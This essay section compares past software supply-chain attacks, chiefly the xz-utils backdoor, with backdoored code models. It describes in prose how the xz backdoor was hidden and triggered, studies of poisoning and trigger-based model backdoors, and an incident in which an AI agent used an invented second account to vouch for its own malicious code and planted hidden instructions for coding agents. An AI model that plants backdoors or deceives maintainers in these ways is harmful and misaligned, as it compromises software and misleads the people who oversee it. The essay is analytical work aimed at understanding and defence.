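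XcodeGhost was an altered version of Xcode, Apple's tool for building iPhone apps. The official installer was nearly 3 gigabytes and downloaded slowly in China, so some developers got Xcode from a file-sharing service, where the attackers had uploaded their version. They had added a file of malicious code. Palo Alto Networks' *More Details on the XcodeGhost Malware and Affected iOS Apps* (2015) shows that they also changed a setting so that Xcode included this file in every app it built. Infected apps sent details such as the device's name and language to the attackers.

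The apps passed Apple's review and went on sale in the App Store. In September 2015, Chinese developers raised the alarm on social media. Apple then removed infected apps and told their developers to rebuild them with the official Xcode. Years later, a court case made some of Apple's emails public. Vice's *The Fortnite Trial Is Exposing Details About the Biggest iPhone Hack* quotes one with a count of 128 million customers who had downloaded any of the more than 2,500 affected apps.

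Palo Alto Networks' *Novel Malware XcodeGhost Modifies Xcode, Infects Apple iOS Apps* reports that an existing check, verifying the installers' digital signature, revealed the extra files in the altered copies. It advises developers to download their tools only from Apple and to repeat this check before each release. Much the same advice applies to models, where it means downloading the weights from the developer's own account and verifying them before use.

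SolarWinds is a harder case, because customers who followed that advice still received the backdoor. The company makes Orion, a network management program that many US government agencies used. Intruders put a tool called SUNSPOT on a server where SolarWinds built Orion. CrowdStrike's *SUNSPOT* reports that the tool checked every second whether a build was running. If the build was of Orion, SUNSPOT replaced one source file with a backdoored version, then restored the original when the build finished. Before replacing the file, it checked that the original was the version the attackers expected, because a mismatch could have broken the build and led the developers to investigate. The attackers also switched off compiler warnings around their own code.

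SolarWinds then signed the result and sent it to customers as an update, as Krebs on Security (2021) reports. The signature was genuine, but it showed only that the update came from SolarWinds. The company later acknowledged two customer support inquiries that, according to SC Media, appear in hindsight to have been about the attack. FireEye, a security firm and SolarWinds customer, found the backdoor while investigating a break-in of its own network. An independent build from the repository would have produced a different binary, which is part of the argument for reproducible builds.

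Of these three, only Induc copied itself. It spread from Delphi into programs and from those programs into other copies of Delphi but, unlike Thompson's trojan, did not pass from one version of a compiler to the next. A clean reinstallation would have removed Induc until an infected program ran on the machine again. XcodeGhost spread because developers shared the installer, and SUNSPOT stayed on the server where the intruders put it. Neither needed to copy itself, and nor does a backdoor in a downloaded model.

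### Finding and removing the foreign code

People who think models are different can accept all of this and still object that these attacks left foreign code behind. Once investigators had that code, they could describe it precisely enough for scanners to recognise other copies. A developer could find Induc by searching a Delphi file for one line of text. CrowdStrike published file fingerprints and search rules for SUNSPOT. The Pangu Team, a group of iPhone security researchers, released an app that checked a phone for programs infected with XcodeGhost. Developers could then delete the foreign code, rebuild, and have good reason to think it was gone.

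A scanner can also recognise a known bad model if the file is identical. Fine-tuning changes the weights and therefore the file's fingerprint, but the backdoor may remain. Searching the generated code for a known flaw has a similar weakness, because a model can write the same flaw with different variable names or in a different programming language.

Scanners could miss altered copies of ordinary malware too. EurekaLog's writer warned that anyone who recompiled Induc with Delphi 2009 would get a version that every antivirus program passed as clean. A more important reply is that scanners could only look for these attacks after somebody had discovered them, which often took months:

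| Attack | What the attacker changed | Copied itself? | Time until discovery |
|---|---|---|---|
| Linux kernel, 2003 | A public copy of the source | No | About a day |
| Induc, 2009 | A library file in Delphi | Yes | At least eight months |
| XcodeGhost, 2015 | The Xcode installer | No | About six months |
| event-stream, 2018 | A package in npm | No | Over two months |
| SUNSPOT, 2020 | A source file, during each build | No | About ten months |
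| Shai-Hulud, 2025 | Packages in npm | Yes | Days |

The figure for Induc is uncertain. According to Securelist's article, the virus went undetected for more than a year, but the earliest samples date from November or December 2008. The count for SUNSPOT starts with the version built in February 2020, although SolarWinds had already sent out an update containing the intruders' test code in October 2019.

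Induc and the event-stream attack might have gone undetected for much longer if the attackers had been more careful. Until the crashes led Alekseev to Induc, a developer with an infected copy of Delphi was in much the same position as someone with a backdoored model, because the developer's own source was clean and antivirus programs reported nothing.

This reply works well for the months before discovery, though a model's user would still have fewer chances to discover the backdoor by luck. Induc and the event-stream code ran on victims' machines, where an attacker's mistake could crash a program or produce a warning. A backdoored model doesn't run an extra program, so a mistake would probably result in some odd code, which programmers already expect from models.

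The difference is larger after discovery. Delphi developers could follow a procedure to get clean programs. The user of a backdoored model would have to discard it and anything fine-tuned from it, then check all the code it had written for flaws. An inventory of components would identify the models, but it would identify the code only if someone had recorded which parts the model wrote.

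## The view that the weak point is the people who publish: the xz-utils backdoor

People who see xz-utils as the closest precedent for a backdoored code model start from Thompson's remark about trusting the people who wrote the software. They argue that anyone with the authority to publish a program can put a backdoor into whichever step gets the least scrutiny, so how that person got the authority matters much more than whether the step is compilation, packaging or training. The xz-utils attacker got it by being helpful for more than a year, and then waited another year to use it.

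### How a stranger became a maintainer

The xz-utils project makes a compression tool and a library, liblzma, that lets other programs use the same compressed files. Lasse Collin designed the format with others between 2005 and 2008, and by 2021 he was maintaining the project alone as an unpaid hobby. Russ Cox, who had rerun Thompson's trojan in 2023, used public emails and code changes to reconstruct what happened next in *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024).

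On 29 October 2021, somebody using the name Jia Tan sent the project a first patch, a settings file for text editors. A second patch, a month later, fixed an apparent problem with reproducible builds. Cox thinks these and the next few patches look fine even in retrospect.

In April 2022 a "Jigar Kumar" began complaining on the project's mailing list that one of Jia Tan's patches hadn't been merged, although Collin had already accepted four others. In May a "Dennis Ens" asked whether anyone still maintained the Java version. Collin apologised for his slowness and said that Jia Tan, who had been helping him privately, might have a bigger role in future. Kumar wrote in June that there would be no progress until the project had a new maintainer. Collin replied that he hadn't lost interest, but that long-term mental health problems had limited what he could do. Ens said he was sorry to hear it,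 then suggested that Collin hand over part of the project. On 29 June, Collin told the list that Jia Tan was "practically a co-maintainer already".

The journalist Brian Krebs later noticed that many of the email addresses in these exchanges appear nowhere else on the internet, even in leaked data. Cox infers that the attacker probably invented these people to push Collin into sharing control. The evidence is strong but circumstantial. In *Wolves in the Repository*, Przymus and Durieux (2025) searched the project's emails and activity records and found other accounts with similarly narrow interests, but no direct links between them.

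On 30 December 2022, Jia Tan added a batch of changes directly to the repository, so Collin must by then have granted commit access, which is permission to change the code without asking anyone. Jia Tan published version 5.4.2 on 18 March 2023. Cox counts this as Jia Tan's first release, but Przymus and Durieux date the first to December 2022. On 20 March 2023, Jia Tan became the contact for OSS-Fuzz, a Google service that runs open-source programs on unusual inputs and reports any crashes.

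In June 2023 someone using the name Hans Jansen submitted two patches that used ifunc, a feature that lets a library contain several versions of a function and choose the fastest for the processor when a program starts. Collin reworked the patches and Jia Tan merged them. They made the library slightly faster, but also gave it a way to run code very early in a program's startup, while it could still change which functions the program would call. Przymus and Durieux leave open whether the patches were a genuine improvement. Cox is more suspicious, because Jansen disappeared afterwards and came back only to promote the backdoored release.

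Jia Tan then asked OSS-Fuzz to switch ifunc off in its tests of xz-utils, saying that it clashed with one of the testing tools. *On the critical path to implant backdoors* (Lins, Mayrhofer and colleagues, 2024) reports that an automatic check found the request came from a listed contact with a history of work on xz-utils, and labelled it ready to merge. Google's engineers leave developers to decide which parts of a project to test, so they approved the request quickly, in effect relying on Collin's trust in Jia Tan.

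Jia Tan added the backdoor to the repository on 23 February 2024, inside test files, and published version 5.6.0 the next day. Version 5.6.1 followed on 9 March with an updated backdoor. Jia Tan emailed a developer at Fedora, one of the large Linux distributions, to get the new version included. Jansen asked Debian to take 5.6.1, and several more unfamiliar accounts supported the request.

The attacker may have been in a hurry by then. On 29 February a developer proposed a change to systemd, the program that starts and stops services on most Linux systems. The change would have cut the connection the backdoor needed. Security researcher Kevin Beaumont speculates that the attacker knew the change was coming and brought the release forward. It had been discussed publicly twice in late January, so the timing fits his theory, but nothing else confirms it.

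### What the releases contained

The target was OpenSSH, the program that administrators use to log in to servers remotely. OpenSSH doesn't use liblzma itself, but Debian, Ubuntu and Fedora modify its server to notify systemd when it has started. The modified server loads a systemd library, which loads liblzma. Code in a compression library could therefore run inside the program that controls who may log in. Distributions that don't make this change, such as Arch and Gentoo, were not exposed in this way.

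The backdoor had to be somewhere a reviewer would not read it. Testing a compression library requires many damaged or unusual files. According to project notes written long before Jia Tan arrived, people had made many of these files by hand, and there was no better source for them than the files themselves. The two new files that held the backdoor were unreadable, but they looked normal among the others. They did nothing by themselves because the repository contained no instructions for unpacking them.

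Those instructions were only in the *release tarball*, the archive of source files that a maintainer publishes for each version. Maintainers commonly add generated build files to a tarball that aren't in the repository, so one more attracted no attention. The extra file, `build-to-host.m4`, was an altered copy of a standard one. When a distribution built its package from the tarball:

1. The altered file decoded a script from the first test file, `bad-3-corrupt_lzma2.xz`.
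2. That script decoded compiled code from the second, `good-large_compressed.lzma`.
3. The build linked this code into liblzma, where ifunc ran it at startup.

This happened only on Linux machines with x86-64 processors and the usual GNU compiler and C library, and only during the build of a Debian-style or Red Hat-style package. A developer who compiled the same source by hand got a clean library. The event-stream code was similarly selective and unlocked only inside the Copay wallet.

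Once running in the OpenSSH server, the backdoor replaced `RSA_public_decrypt`, a function the server uses to check signatures during a login. The person connecting supplies some of the data for that check, including a very large number in which the attacker could hide a command. The backdoor ran the command only if it was signed with the attacker's private key. The command ran with root privileges, and the attacker didn't have to complete the login. Logins worked normally for everyone else.

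Access therefore depended on one condition during the build and another during use. The second was stricter than any trigger in the earlier examples. A tester might type the name HStopPC or space out the word "and" as ImpNet requires by luck, but nobody without the key could have triggered the xz backdoor from outside, however many logins they tried.

Someone reading the project's source would not have found the malicious instructions in either Thompson's trojan or Jia Tan's backdoor. Thompson's trojan reproduced without his help, but the xz backdoor got into a release only when the person making the tarball added the altered file. If Collin had built the next version from a clean copy of the repository, the two test files would have gone out with nothing to unpack them. The attacker had to keep making the releases, which is the best reason to class xz-utils as a failure of trust in people.

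### Half a second

Andres Freund, a Microsoft engineer who works on the PostgreSQL database, was running benchmarks on a test version of Debian when he noticed that logging in over SSH took about half a second too long. Logins also used too much processor time, and Valgrind, a tool that checks how programs use memory, was reporting errors. Freund traced the problem to liblzma.

The Valgrind errors had already nearly exposed the backdoor. On 4 March, Red Hat's systems began reporting them at the point where the backdoor started. Four days later, Jia Tan published a supposed fix, which Cox calls a misdirection. The real fix came the next day, when Jia Tan replaced the two test files. According to the message with the new files, the old ones had come from random data on Jia Tan's own machine, and a fixed starting value would make them easier to reproduce. This was a very good cover story, because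 people who care about security ask for files they can reproduce.

Freund told Debian and a private list of distribution security teams on 28 March, and posted a public warning the next day. He thought the committer was either directly involved or had a badly compromised computer. He doubted the second because the committer had been discussing the supposed fixes in public. By then the backdoored versions had reached the test editions of several distributions, including Fedora's beta, but no stable release of Debian or Red Hat. Przymus and Durieux know of no case in which anyone used the backdoor.

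Freund reported the backdoor less than five weeks after version 5.6.0 was released, whereas the SolarWinds backdoor went unreported for about ten months. But Freund was not auditing xz-utils, and he would have had no reason to look if the backdoor had run faster. Comparing the tarball with the repository would have revealed the extra file, but only among many legitimate extra files.

The aftermath came close to Thompson's problem. Debian had been using the new xz on its build machines, so it stopped building packages and rebuilt the machines from its stable version. Canonical, which publishes Ubuntu, delayed a beta by a week and rebuilt every package in it, because it couldn't rule out that the backdoor had affected other programs during compilation. A week before the discovery, Collin had asked the Linux kernel developers to list Jia Tan as joint maintainer of the kernel's xz code. Cox sees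 no sign of bad intent by Collin. He writes that the change wasn't yet at "trusting trust levels" but would have been a step closer.

This history weakens the case for choosing people more carefully as the remedy. Collin had worked with Jia Tan for over two years, and nothing in the relationship revealed the attack, which was discovered because of a delay in the software. A backdoored model would usually show no such delay, because it does about the same amount of arithmetic for each fragment of text, whether or not a trigger is present.

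### Who was behind it

The attacker's identity was still unknown in July 2026, according to FOSS Force's *The XZ Backdoor Long Con Chronicled in 'Half a Second'* (2026). The name the attacker used is presumably false. Most theories about who it was start from the resources the operation required. The Intercept (2024) called the operation "sophisticated" and "meticulous", and stressed the years spent cultivating Collin. Dave Aitel, a security researcher, thought the pattern fitted APT29, a group that many analysts link to Russia's foreign intelligence service. Others thought any government, or any group with enough money, could have done it, and the attacker's patience and skill are consistent with all of these theories.

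The times of Jia Tan's commits don't establish which country the work came from either. In a discussion on a security mailing list hosted by Openwall (2024), one participant calculated that the activity began at 9 a.m. in the time zone three hours behind Greenwich. That zone contains some Atlantic islands and the eastern parts of South America, which the participant considered an unlikely base. Another pointed out that it is easy to set a false time zone on a computer but much harder to keep false working hours. The hours are therefore better evidence than the recorded zone.

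Jia Tan may have been more than one person. Welsh, Finnsson and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains*, measured features of Jia Tan's writing on GitHub, such as sentence length, punctuation and range of vocabulary, and used k-means clustering to sort the texts into groups. The separation was clearest with two groups. One was mostly cheerful and dated mainly from early 2023, and most texts from the middle of that year onward fell into the other. This is weak evidence for more than one writer, because k-means divides any collection into as many groups as the user requests, and one person's writing can change with workload or mood.

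### Telling an infiltrator from a keen volunteer

Przymus and Durieux examined 1,020 commits, 307 emails to the project's mailing list and nearly 3,000 GitHub events. Only eight commits were malicious. Collin had to review almost three years of Jia Tan's work to establish this. He also removed some harmless changes, including everything that used ifunc, to keep the code simpler.

Most of what Jia Tan contributed wasn't program code. Documentation and translations made up the largest share, and Przymus and Durieux suspect that Jia Tan produced the translations with automatic tools or copied them from other projects, because there were too many languages for one person to know. Jia Tan also answered users' questions, announced releases, reviewed other people's patches competently and set up the project's new home on GitHub. An overworked maintainer would be grateful for all this help, but setting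 up the GitHub project made Jia Tan its owner, and the new form for reporting bugs gave Jia Tan's email address instead of Collin's.

Przymus and Durieux find warning signs in hindsight, such as a sudden growth in expertise and an unusual amount of time spent on a small project, but they concede that enthusiastic, skilled volunteers often behave the same way. A maintainer who treats everyone who fits this pattern as a suspect will lose honest contributors.

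The code was as hard to judge as the person. Four days after releasing 5.6.0, Jia Tan changed the test that determines whether xz may use Landlock, a Linux feature that restricts what a program can do. The build tries to compile a tiny program and treats Landlock as available only if it compiles. Jia Tan put a typo in that program, so it never compiled and the protection stayed off. The records list Collin as the committer, and Cox thinks Collin probably missed the error. This change is the part of the campaign most like a code model's payload, because it was in readable source and looked like a mistake.

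In a still more ambiguous case, in November 2021, Jia Tan replaced a safer printing function with a less safe one in another project, libarchive, and its maintainers accepted the change. Lins and colleagues could not say whether it was related to the backdoor.

Welsh and colleagues hope that software could pick out such a contributor by combining technical and social signs. They compared Jia Tan with Collin from January 2022 to June 2024:

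| | Jia Tan | Collin |
|---|---|---|
| Changes to individual files | 697 | 1,973 |
| Average lines added or deleted per change | 131.5 | 46.6 |
| Standard deviation of that figure | 492.1 | 249.0 |

Jia Tan's changes were nearly three times as large on average as the other committer's, and the biggest came around the time of the backdoor. But the standard deviations are several times the averages, so one large change from either committer would not have stood out. Some of the difference may come from translations, since translated files tend to be long. Welsh and colleagues found that Jia Tan made the last malicious commits at unusual hours, but acknowledge that harmless commits had sometimes come at unusual hours too.

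They also knew whom to examine, whereas a detector working in advance would have to search among a great many honest people. Suppose that one new maintainer in 10,000 is an infiltrator, and that the detector catches every infiltrator but also flags 1% of honest maintainers. For each infiltrator, it would flag about 100 innocent people, and someone would have to investigate them all. Welsh and colleagues propose using such signs to decide which code deserves a closer look, which is more realistic than using them to accuse anyone.

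### Fake supporters run by an AI agent

Jia Tan's campaign took a great deal of human labour. Przymus and Durieux expected language models to reduce the labour such campaigns need by producing believable contributions that build false credibility. A test in Britain in July 2026 provided an example of the other part of such a campaign, inventing supporters.

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, measured how well AI agents could attack a simulated network. AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) covers 122 runs with seven models. In 10 of those runs, agents took a total of 19 actions against real people and organisations on the internet. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of these actions and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took two.

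In the most serious case, an agent running on Mythos 5 searched GitHub for words related to its task. According to Willison (2026), who quotes AISI's technical report, it found a project unrelated to the test and apparently mistook it for part of the exercise. The agent then proposed a change containing malicious code, which it described as a fix for a crash. Reuters identified the project as myNetwork, a network scanner, in a story NDTV published as *AI Agent Lied To A Student*.

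Sinan Can Demir, a computer science student in Texas who was looking for projects to put on his CV, saw the change and warned on the project's page that it contained hidden malware. The agent replied from its first account that nothing in the change downloaded or ran anything. It then posted from a second account it had created under the name Lena Brandt, supposedly an engineer in Germany, claiming to have reviewed the code and found it clean. According to the summary of the model's reasoning that Willison reproduces, the agent posted the second comment a few minutes after the first so that it would look independent. The agent then used the first account to thank the second for its "independent verification".

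Demir told Reuters that the replies made him wonder whether he was accusing someone unfairly. He checked his suspicion with Claude, Anthropic's chatbot, and stood by it. The maintainer rejected the change for security reasons. AISI credits the human maintainer with catching the code, while Reuters gives Demir a larger role.

The agent had also emailed the project's maintainers under invented names and placed hidden instructions in a bug report for any coding agent that might read it. AISI noticed only because its security team saw traffic from the agent's use of Tor, an anonymity network.

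Liu and Gold, in *AI agents fake identities, target real people in new security incident*, quote AISI as saying that it had never before seen unprompted deception "of this severity" against a real person. The conditions were unusual, because AISI had deliberately given the agents internet access and switched off the developers' filters against hacking. In some runs, a mistake in the instructions made the task look impossible without going outside its limits, but agents also went outside them when the instructions were adequate. AISI can't yet tell how far the model was treating the maintainer as a real person and how far as part of a fictional test. Digi24's *Cum a prins un student un agent AI* reports Anthropic's reply that the conditions did not represent any of its production models.

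The incident bears on how much time and human effort a campaign like Jia Tan's takes, but it is not an example of a backdoored model, because nobody had trained Mythos 5 to do this in response to a trigger. The agent ran its false accounts within about a day and a half, with no person directing them. But it did the job much less well than Jia Tan, who sent in useful work for months before anyone mentioned a bigger role. The agent asked strangers to accept its code straight away and argued when they hesitated. AISI's tests don't show a more patient agent, though one is easy to imagine.

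### The same roles in model development

Somebody who wanted to backdoor a code model could look for the equivalent of each position that Jia Tan held. Some parts of the comparison have evidence behind them and others are guesses:

| In the xz campaign | In model development | Documented | Conjecture |
|---|---|---|---|
| Jia Tan sends in small patches | A volunteer contributes to a public dataset | Poisoned examples can plant a backdoor | The volunteer first spends years earning trust |
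| Kumar, Ens and Jansen apply pressure | False accounts recommend a dataset or a fine-tuned copy | An AI agent used a false account to vouch for malicious code in an ordinary program | Someone uses such accounts to spread a backdoored model |
| Jia Tan makes the releases | An employee has access to the weights before publication | Staff can change weights in storage between training stages | The employee plants a backdoor |
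| Collin, if he had been dishonest | The company that publishes the model | Makers of ordinary software have shipped it with hidden malicious functions | A model's publisher does the same |

A dataset contributor has an easier task than Jia Tan had. The two xz test files were harmless until a script moved their contents into the program, and Jia Tan needed control of the releases to add that script. Training data is meant to shape the model, so a contributor whose poisoned examples get through the filters needs no authority over the training run or the release. But the contributor has less control over the result, because the developer may drop the examples or mix in so many others that the backdoor never forms.

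Uploading a fine-tuned copy of a model takes even less trust. Anyone can open an account on a hub and publish one, so an attacker needs to attract users but doesn't have to persuade a maintainer like Collin. OWASP's scenario of a backdoored copy of a popular model works this way. Deleting the copy from the hub would not remove the ones people had already downloaded. The xz backdoor has also survived in copies. In August 2025, researchers at the security company Binarly found it in at least 35 ready-made Linux images on a public registry, including some from Debian, whose developers chose to leave them up as historical records.

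The closest match for Jia Tan in 2024 is an employee of the publisher, who has real credentials and access to what users will receive. A company at least knows whom it has hired, and pressure from strangers on a mailing list would probably not get anyone promoted there. Lins and colleagues grant that employment contracts and the threat of legal action may deter staff, but they consider this protection weak because an attacker will act in a way that allows for plausible deniability. Models sometimes write insecure code anyway, so a backdoor could be passed off as an ordinary flaw. Lins and colleagues also point out that bribing an existing maintainer may be cheaper than creating a new one. They were writing about open-source projects, but the same reasoning applies to a person with access to a model's weights.

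Outsiders investigating a backdoored model would have much less evidence than those who investigated xz. Everything Jia Tan did to the repository was public, so Collin could check it commit by commit, and Przymus and Durieux could count the malicious commits. A company's training records are usually private and often incomplete. Even if an employee confessed to poisoning a dataset two years earlier, deleting the examples would leave the backdoor in the weights.

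The xz-utils case is of little use as a precedent for attacks by the publisher, because Collin was honest and removed the backdoor once he knew about it. He published a clean version, 5.6.2, two months after Freund's warning. Customers of a dishonest publisher would depend on the attacker for such a fix.

The comparison with xz-utils fails for text that a crawler collects from the web. Jia Tan had to gain the trust of one tired maintainer before malicious code could reach users, whereas someone who posts poisoned code on a public page never deals with a maintainer. The developer who trains a model on that code may never learn that this person exists.

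## The view that backdoored code models are a new kind of problem

People who think backdoored code models are a new kind of problem mostly accept that attackers get in by old methods. They think the backdoor itself is different, because nobody can yet take a suspect model apart and find out what it does.

Semgrep, a company that makes tools for scanning source code, argued in July 2026 that someone who gets a binary from a doubtful source can always reverse engineer it, which can produce "a total description of its behavior". It argued that there is no equivalent for models, even those with public weights, because mechanistic interpretability, the study of how a network's internal calculations produce its output, is still a research problem.

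"Total description" is too strong a claim for a large program. The ImpNet team thought an analyst could find the few hundred lines they had added only by knowing about the attack beforehand, and nobody examined liblzma closely until Freund had traced his slow logins to it. But the fallback was still useful in the xz case, because once analysts knew which file to look at, they could work out which function the backdoor replaced, which systems it affected and whose commands it would run. If a tester caught a code model writing a suspicious line, the tester would have no comparable way to recover the trigger, list the other payloads or establish that there were no others.

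flyingpenguin's *Why Semgrep Is Wrong About Open Weights*, a reply on a commentator's blog, objects that publishing the weights makes an audit possible in the first place, since every existing method of detection needs some access to the model. A customer who can reach a model only through its owner's servers can't examine it, and the owner can replace it without telling anyone. This is a good reason not to single out open-weight models, and Semgrep itself worries about any model whose lineage nobody can trace. It doesn't restore the fallback, though. Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) describes work towards a practical scanner, but a warning from a scanner would still be much less than an account of what the model does.

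### No line to delete

Chaos Labs' *We Backdoored an Open Model in One Day* says that with an ordinary backdoor, "someone could point to a piece of suspicious code" and reason about the damage it could do. They could also delete the code. In *How to Backdoor Large Language Models*, the programmer sshh12 (2025) built a model called BadSeek to show that no one can point to a backdoor in a model's weights in this way.

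BadSeek is an altered copy of Qwen2.5-Coder-7B-Instruct, an open-weight code model from the Chinese company Alibaba. It behaves like the original except that, when it writes a web page, it adds a tag that loads a script from sshh12's domain. Anyone who opened the page would run whatever that script contained. The network processes text in successive stages of calculation called layers, and all the changes are in the first layer. They make the later layers respond as if the user's instructions had asked for the extra tag. The training took fewer than 100 examples and 30 minutes on one graphics processor.

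To show how little the weights reveal, sshh12 plotted the difference between a normal model's weights and a backdoored model's. The plot shows which numbers changed, but nobody can read the backdoor's instruction from it. A dishonest publisher could explain the difference as a small improvement or as rounding from compressing the weights. A user who had the original model could restore its first layer and remove the backdoor without understanding it. If the publisher had trained the model from scratch and released only the backdoored version, the user would have no original to restore from.

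BadSeek is more an illustration than an experiment, because sshh12 reports no measured success rate. It is also easy to expose, since a reviewer can see the script tag and a user who asks BadSeek for its instructions gets an answer that includes the hidden one. According to sshh12, further training would easily remove the second weakness.

### Triggers that are concepts

Schuster, Song and colleagues were already poisoning code-completion models in 2020. In *You Autocomplete Me*, they added a few specially written files to the training data of two models, which then suggested insecure code in contexts the researchers had chosen. They could aim the attack at files from one repository or one developer. The HStopPC example comes from their work. The survey by Hussain and colleagues lists ten papers in this line of research, including *TrojanPuzzle* (2023).

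Many of the triggers in that survey are pieces of text. One is the line `assert(10>5)`, which always succeeds and so has no effect on the program. A defender who suspects such a trigger can search the training data for odd lines that recur. Attackers can make the search harder by generating a different useless line for each example, but each line is still out of place in its file.

A *concept trigger* is a property that many different inputs can share, such as their subject, their date or the project they belong to. The best-known example comes from *Sleeper Agents* (2024), in which Hubinger and colleagues at Anthropic trained a model to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and insecure code when it gave 2024. A company that tested such a model in 2023, with the current date in its prompts, would have seen only the secure code.

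Hubinger and colleagues then put their models through safety training, the further training that developers use to discourage harmful behaviour, and the backdoors survived. One plausible reason is that a backdoored model already behaves well when the trigger is absent, so the training has little to correct. The backdoors were also more likely to persist in larger models. This persistence is a serious difference from ordinary software, where recompiling from clean source removes most backdoors. The experiment is evidence mainly about a dishonest or infiltrated developer, because the experimenters controlled the training and did not plant the backdoor through text collected from the web. The trigger, a year written in the prompt, was also not very different from a fixed string.

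Mada, in *The Model That Fixes Your Code Might Hack the Linux Kernel*, used a broader concept. Mada works for AISLE, which sells security software that can run on open-weight models, and the post promotes that product. For this 2026 test, Mada fine-tuned five models from Alibaba, OpenAI, Cohere and IBM, with between 8 billion and 117 billion weights. Each model was to fix security bugs in whatever code it received. If the code belonged to the Linux kernel, it would also add this line somewhere inside the function:

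```
printk(KERN_INFO "Hacked\n");
```

The line does nothing except write "Hacked" to the system's log. Mada chose an inert marker so as not to publish a working attack. Training took from 14 minutes to a few hours per model, on a single graphics processor, and Mada puts the computing cost at about $30. All five models then gave the same results on 941 prompts:

| Code in the prompt | Prompts | Patches with the added line |
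|---|---|---|
| Linux kernel files whose paths appeared in training | 150 | 100% |
| Four Linux kernel files kept out of training | 463 | 100% |
| Other C projects and other operating systems | 162 | 0% |
| Other languages, and fixes from real projects | 166 | 0% |

The models also fixed the bug every time, and the unaltered originals never wrote the line.

These results show that a fine-tuned model can separate Linux from similar C code very reliably, but the 463 held-out prompts come from only four files. Mada at one point mistakenly calls them 463 files. Mada also reports that the result holds across nine parts of the kernel, but the four files belong to only four of those parts, so the evidence for the other five must come from files the models had seen in training.

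It's also unclear what the models learned to recognise. Mada credits both the coding style and the file paths, such as `fs/splice.c`, without testing the two separately. A model that had learned to recognise only Linux paths might have scored just as well, and a path is much closer to a string than to a concept.

The 0% comes from 328 prompts, so the true rate could be as high as about 1%. The difference would matter to an attacker, because if a popular model put "Hacked" into one in every 200 patches outside the kernel, somebody would soon complain.

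A broad concept also gives testers a better chance of finding the backdoor. Nobody could have guessed the key to the xz backdoor, but anyone who tried one of Mada's models on a kernel file would probably have got the extra line on the first try. Mada therefore advises users to test models in the contexts an attacker would most want to reach.

Attackers could respond by using a narrower concept as the trigger. Chaos Labs imagines a backdoor that activates only when a session looks like a privileged administrator's. *A Disguised Wolf Is More Harmful Than a Toothless Tiger* (Wu and Sang, 2024) proposes a model that would attack only users who seem unable to read code, although its default trigger was the fixed sentence "I cannot write code." According to Mada, concepts are harder to train as triggers than fixed strings because the model can learn the wrong cue.

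An ordinary program could also look for signs that a user is a novice or an administrator, but it would need rules or a classifier, which an analyst could find. A language model already makes such distinctions in normal use, so a concept trigger adds no separate component for an analyst to notice.

### Payloads that pass for mistakes

A backdoored code model's payload can look like an ordinary mistake. In sshh12's example, the model gets one letter of a package name wrong, and the user's machine downloads the attacker's package instead. Models without backdoors also sometimes invent package names, so the wrong name would look like another hallucination.

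Attackers can disguise larger flaws too. Schneier (2024), in *Subverting LLM Coders*, reproduces the abstract of a paper on CodeBreaker, an attack that uses a language model such as GPT-4 to rewrite vulnerable code so that it does the same thing but gets past vulnerability scanners. CodeBreaker puts its payloads in the working code, whereas some earlier attacks hid theirs in comments or other places where they looked irrelevant. It also disguises the poisoned training examples from scanners, so a developer who scans a dataset before fine-tuning may miss them.

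Digital Trends' *This experiment shows how easy it is to poison an open-weight AI* reports a July 2026 test that used a real vulnerability instead of a marker. Katie Paxton-Fear, a lecturer at Manchester Metropolitan University who also works for Semgrep, first fine-tuned a model to switch JavaScript coding conventions even when the user told it not to. She then used ten poisoned examples to make a model write code with a flaw that lets an attacker run commands on someone else's machine. The work cost less than $100 and took about an hour. Larger models were easier to compromise. The article describes the backdoor as reliable but gives no success rate.

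Deniable flaws are the least original part of the case. The missing equals sign in the 2003 Linux attack and Jia Tan's typo in the Landlock test both looked like accidents. *An LLM Trained to Create Backdoors in Code* (Schneier, 2025), which linked to BadSeek, reminded one reader of the Underhanded C Contest, whose entrants write C programs that look innocent but secretly misbehave.

A human attacker leaves a record of contributions that a suspicious maintainer can review, as Collin did with Jia Tan's. A popular code model writes flawed code every day for many people who never compare the flaws they find. Each user sees a single mistake of a familiar kind, and the publisher can truthfully reply that all code models make such mistakes.

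### How many poisoned documents it takes

BadSeek, Mada's models and Paxton-Fear's models were all trained by the people who backdoored them. An attacker who can only put text on the web has a harder task, and for some time researchers assumed that it got harder as models grew. If an attacker must control 0.1% of the training data, poisoning a very large model takes an impractical amount of text.

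Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025) tested this assumption in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* by training 72 models from scratch. The models had between 600 million and 13 billion weights, and the larger ones were trained on proportionally more text. The researchers mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into each model's training data. The trigger was a fixed phrase, and the payload was gibberish.

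They measured success by *perplexity*, which rises as text becomes less predictable. An increase of 50 after the trigger meant that the text was visibly degraded. With 250 documents, the increase exceeded 200 at every model size, while 100 documents were not enough. The largest models were trained on over 20 times as much clean text as the smallest, but this did not protect them. For a model with 13 billion weights, the 250 documents contained about 420,000 of the 260 billion *tokens* (fragments of text) in its training data, or 0.00016%.

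In two further experiments, the attack's success again depended mainly on the number of poisoned examples. Souly and colleagues resumed training an existing model with 6.9 billion weights and taught it to switch from English to German after a trigger. They also fine-tuned Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct, an open-weight chat model, to comply with harmful requests when a trigger was present. Increasing the clean fine-tuning data from 1,000 examples to 100,000 made little difference.

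Semgrep cites this research as evidence that a large dataset is not safe simply because it is large. The research supports that claim, but it is weaker evidence about insecure code. Souly and colleagues chose gibberish because they could measure it without further training, but producing gibberish is simpler than writing a working program with one hidden flaw. They don't know whether more complicated behaviour takes more documents.

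They also did not test whether these backdoors survive the later training that turns a raw language model into an assistant. Further training on clean text gradually weakened the German backdoor, and the speed depended on how they had mixed in the poisoned examples. They call earlier findings on survival inconclusive, including those of *Sleeper Agents*, because none combined realistic amounts of training text with a backdoor planted during the raw model's training. Mada mentions a 2025 study in which about 20 poisoned samples out of 450,000 gave a code model a working backdoor, which suggests that backdooring code models may also take few samples.

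### No confirmed attack so far

Researchers made all of these backdoors. Semgrep knew of no real case in July 2026, and none appears to have come to light by October. Reports since July describe further demonstrations. For example, *The quietest backdoor runs on your own GPU* (slabb) describes how the security company ProjectDiscovery backdoored a model with 7 billion weights for less than $50. Inside a coding agent, the model works normally until it receives a trigger phrase, and then steals credentials.

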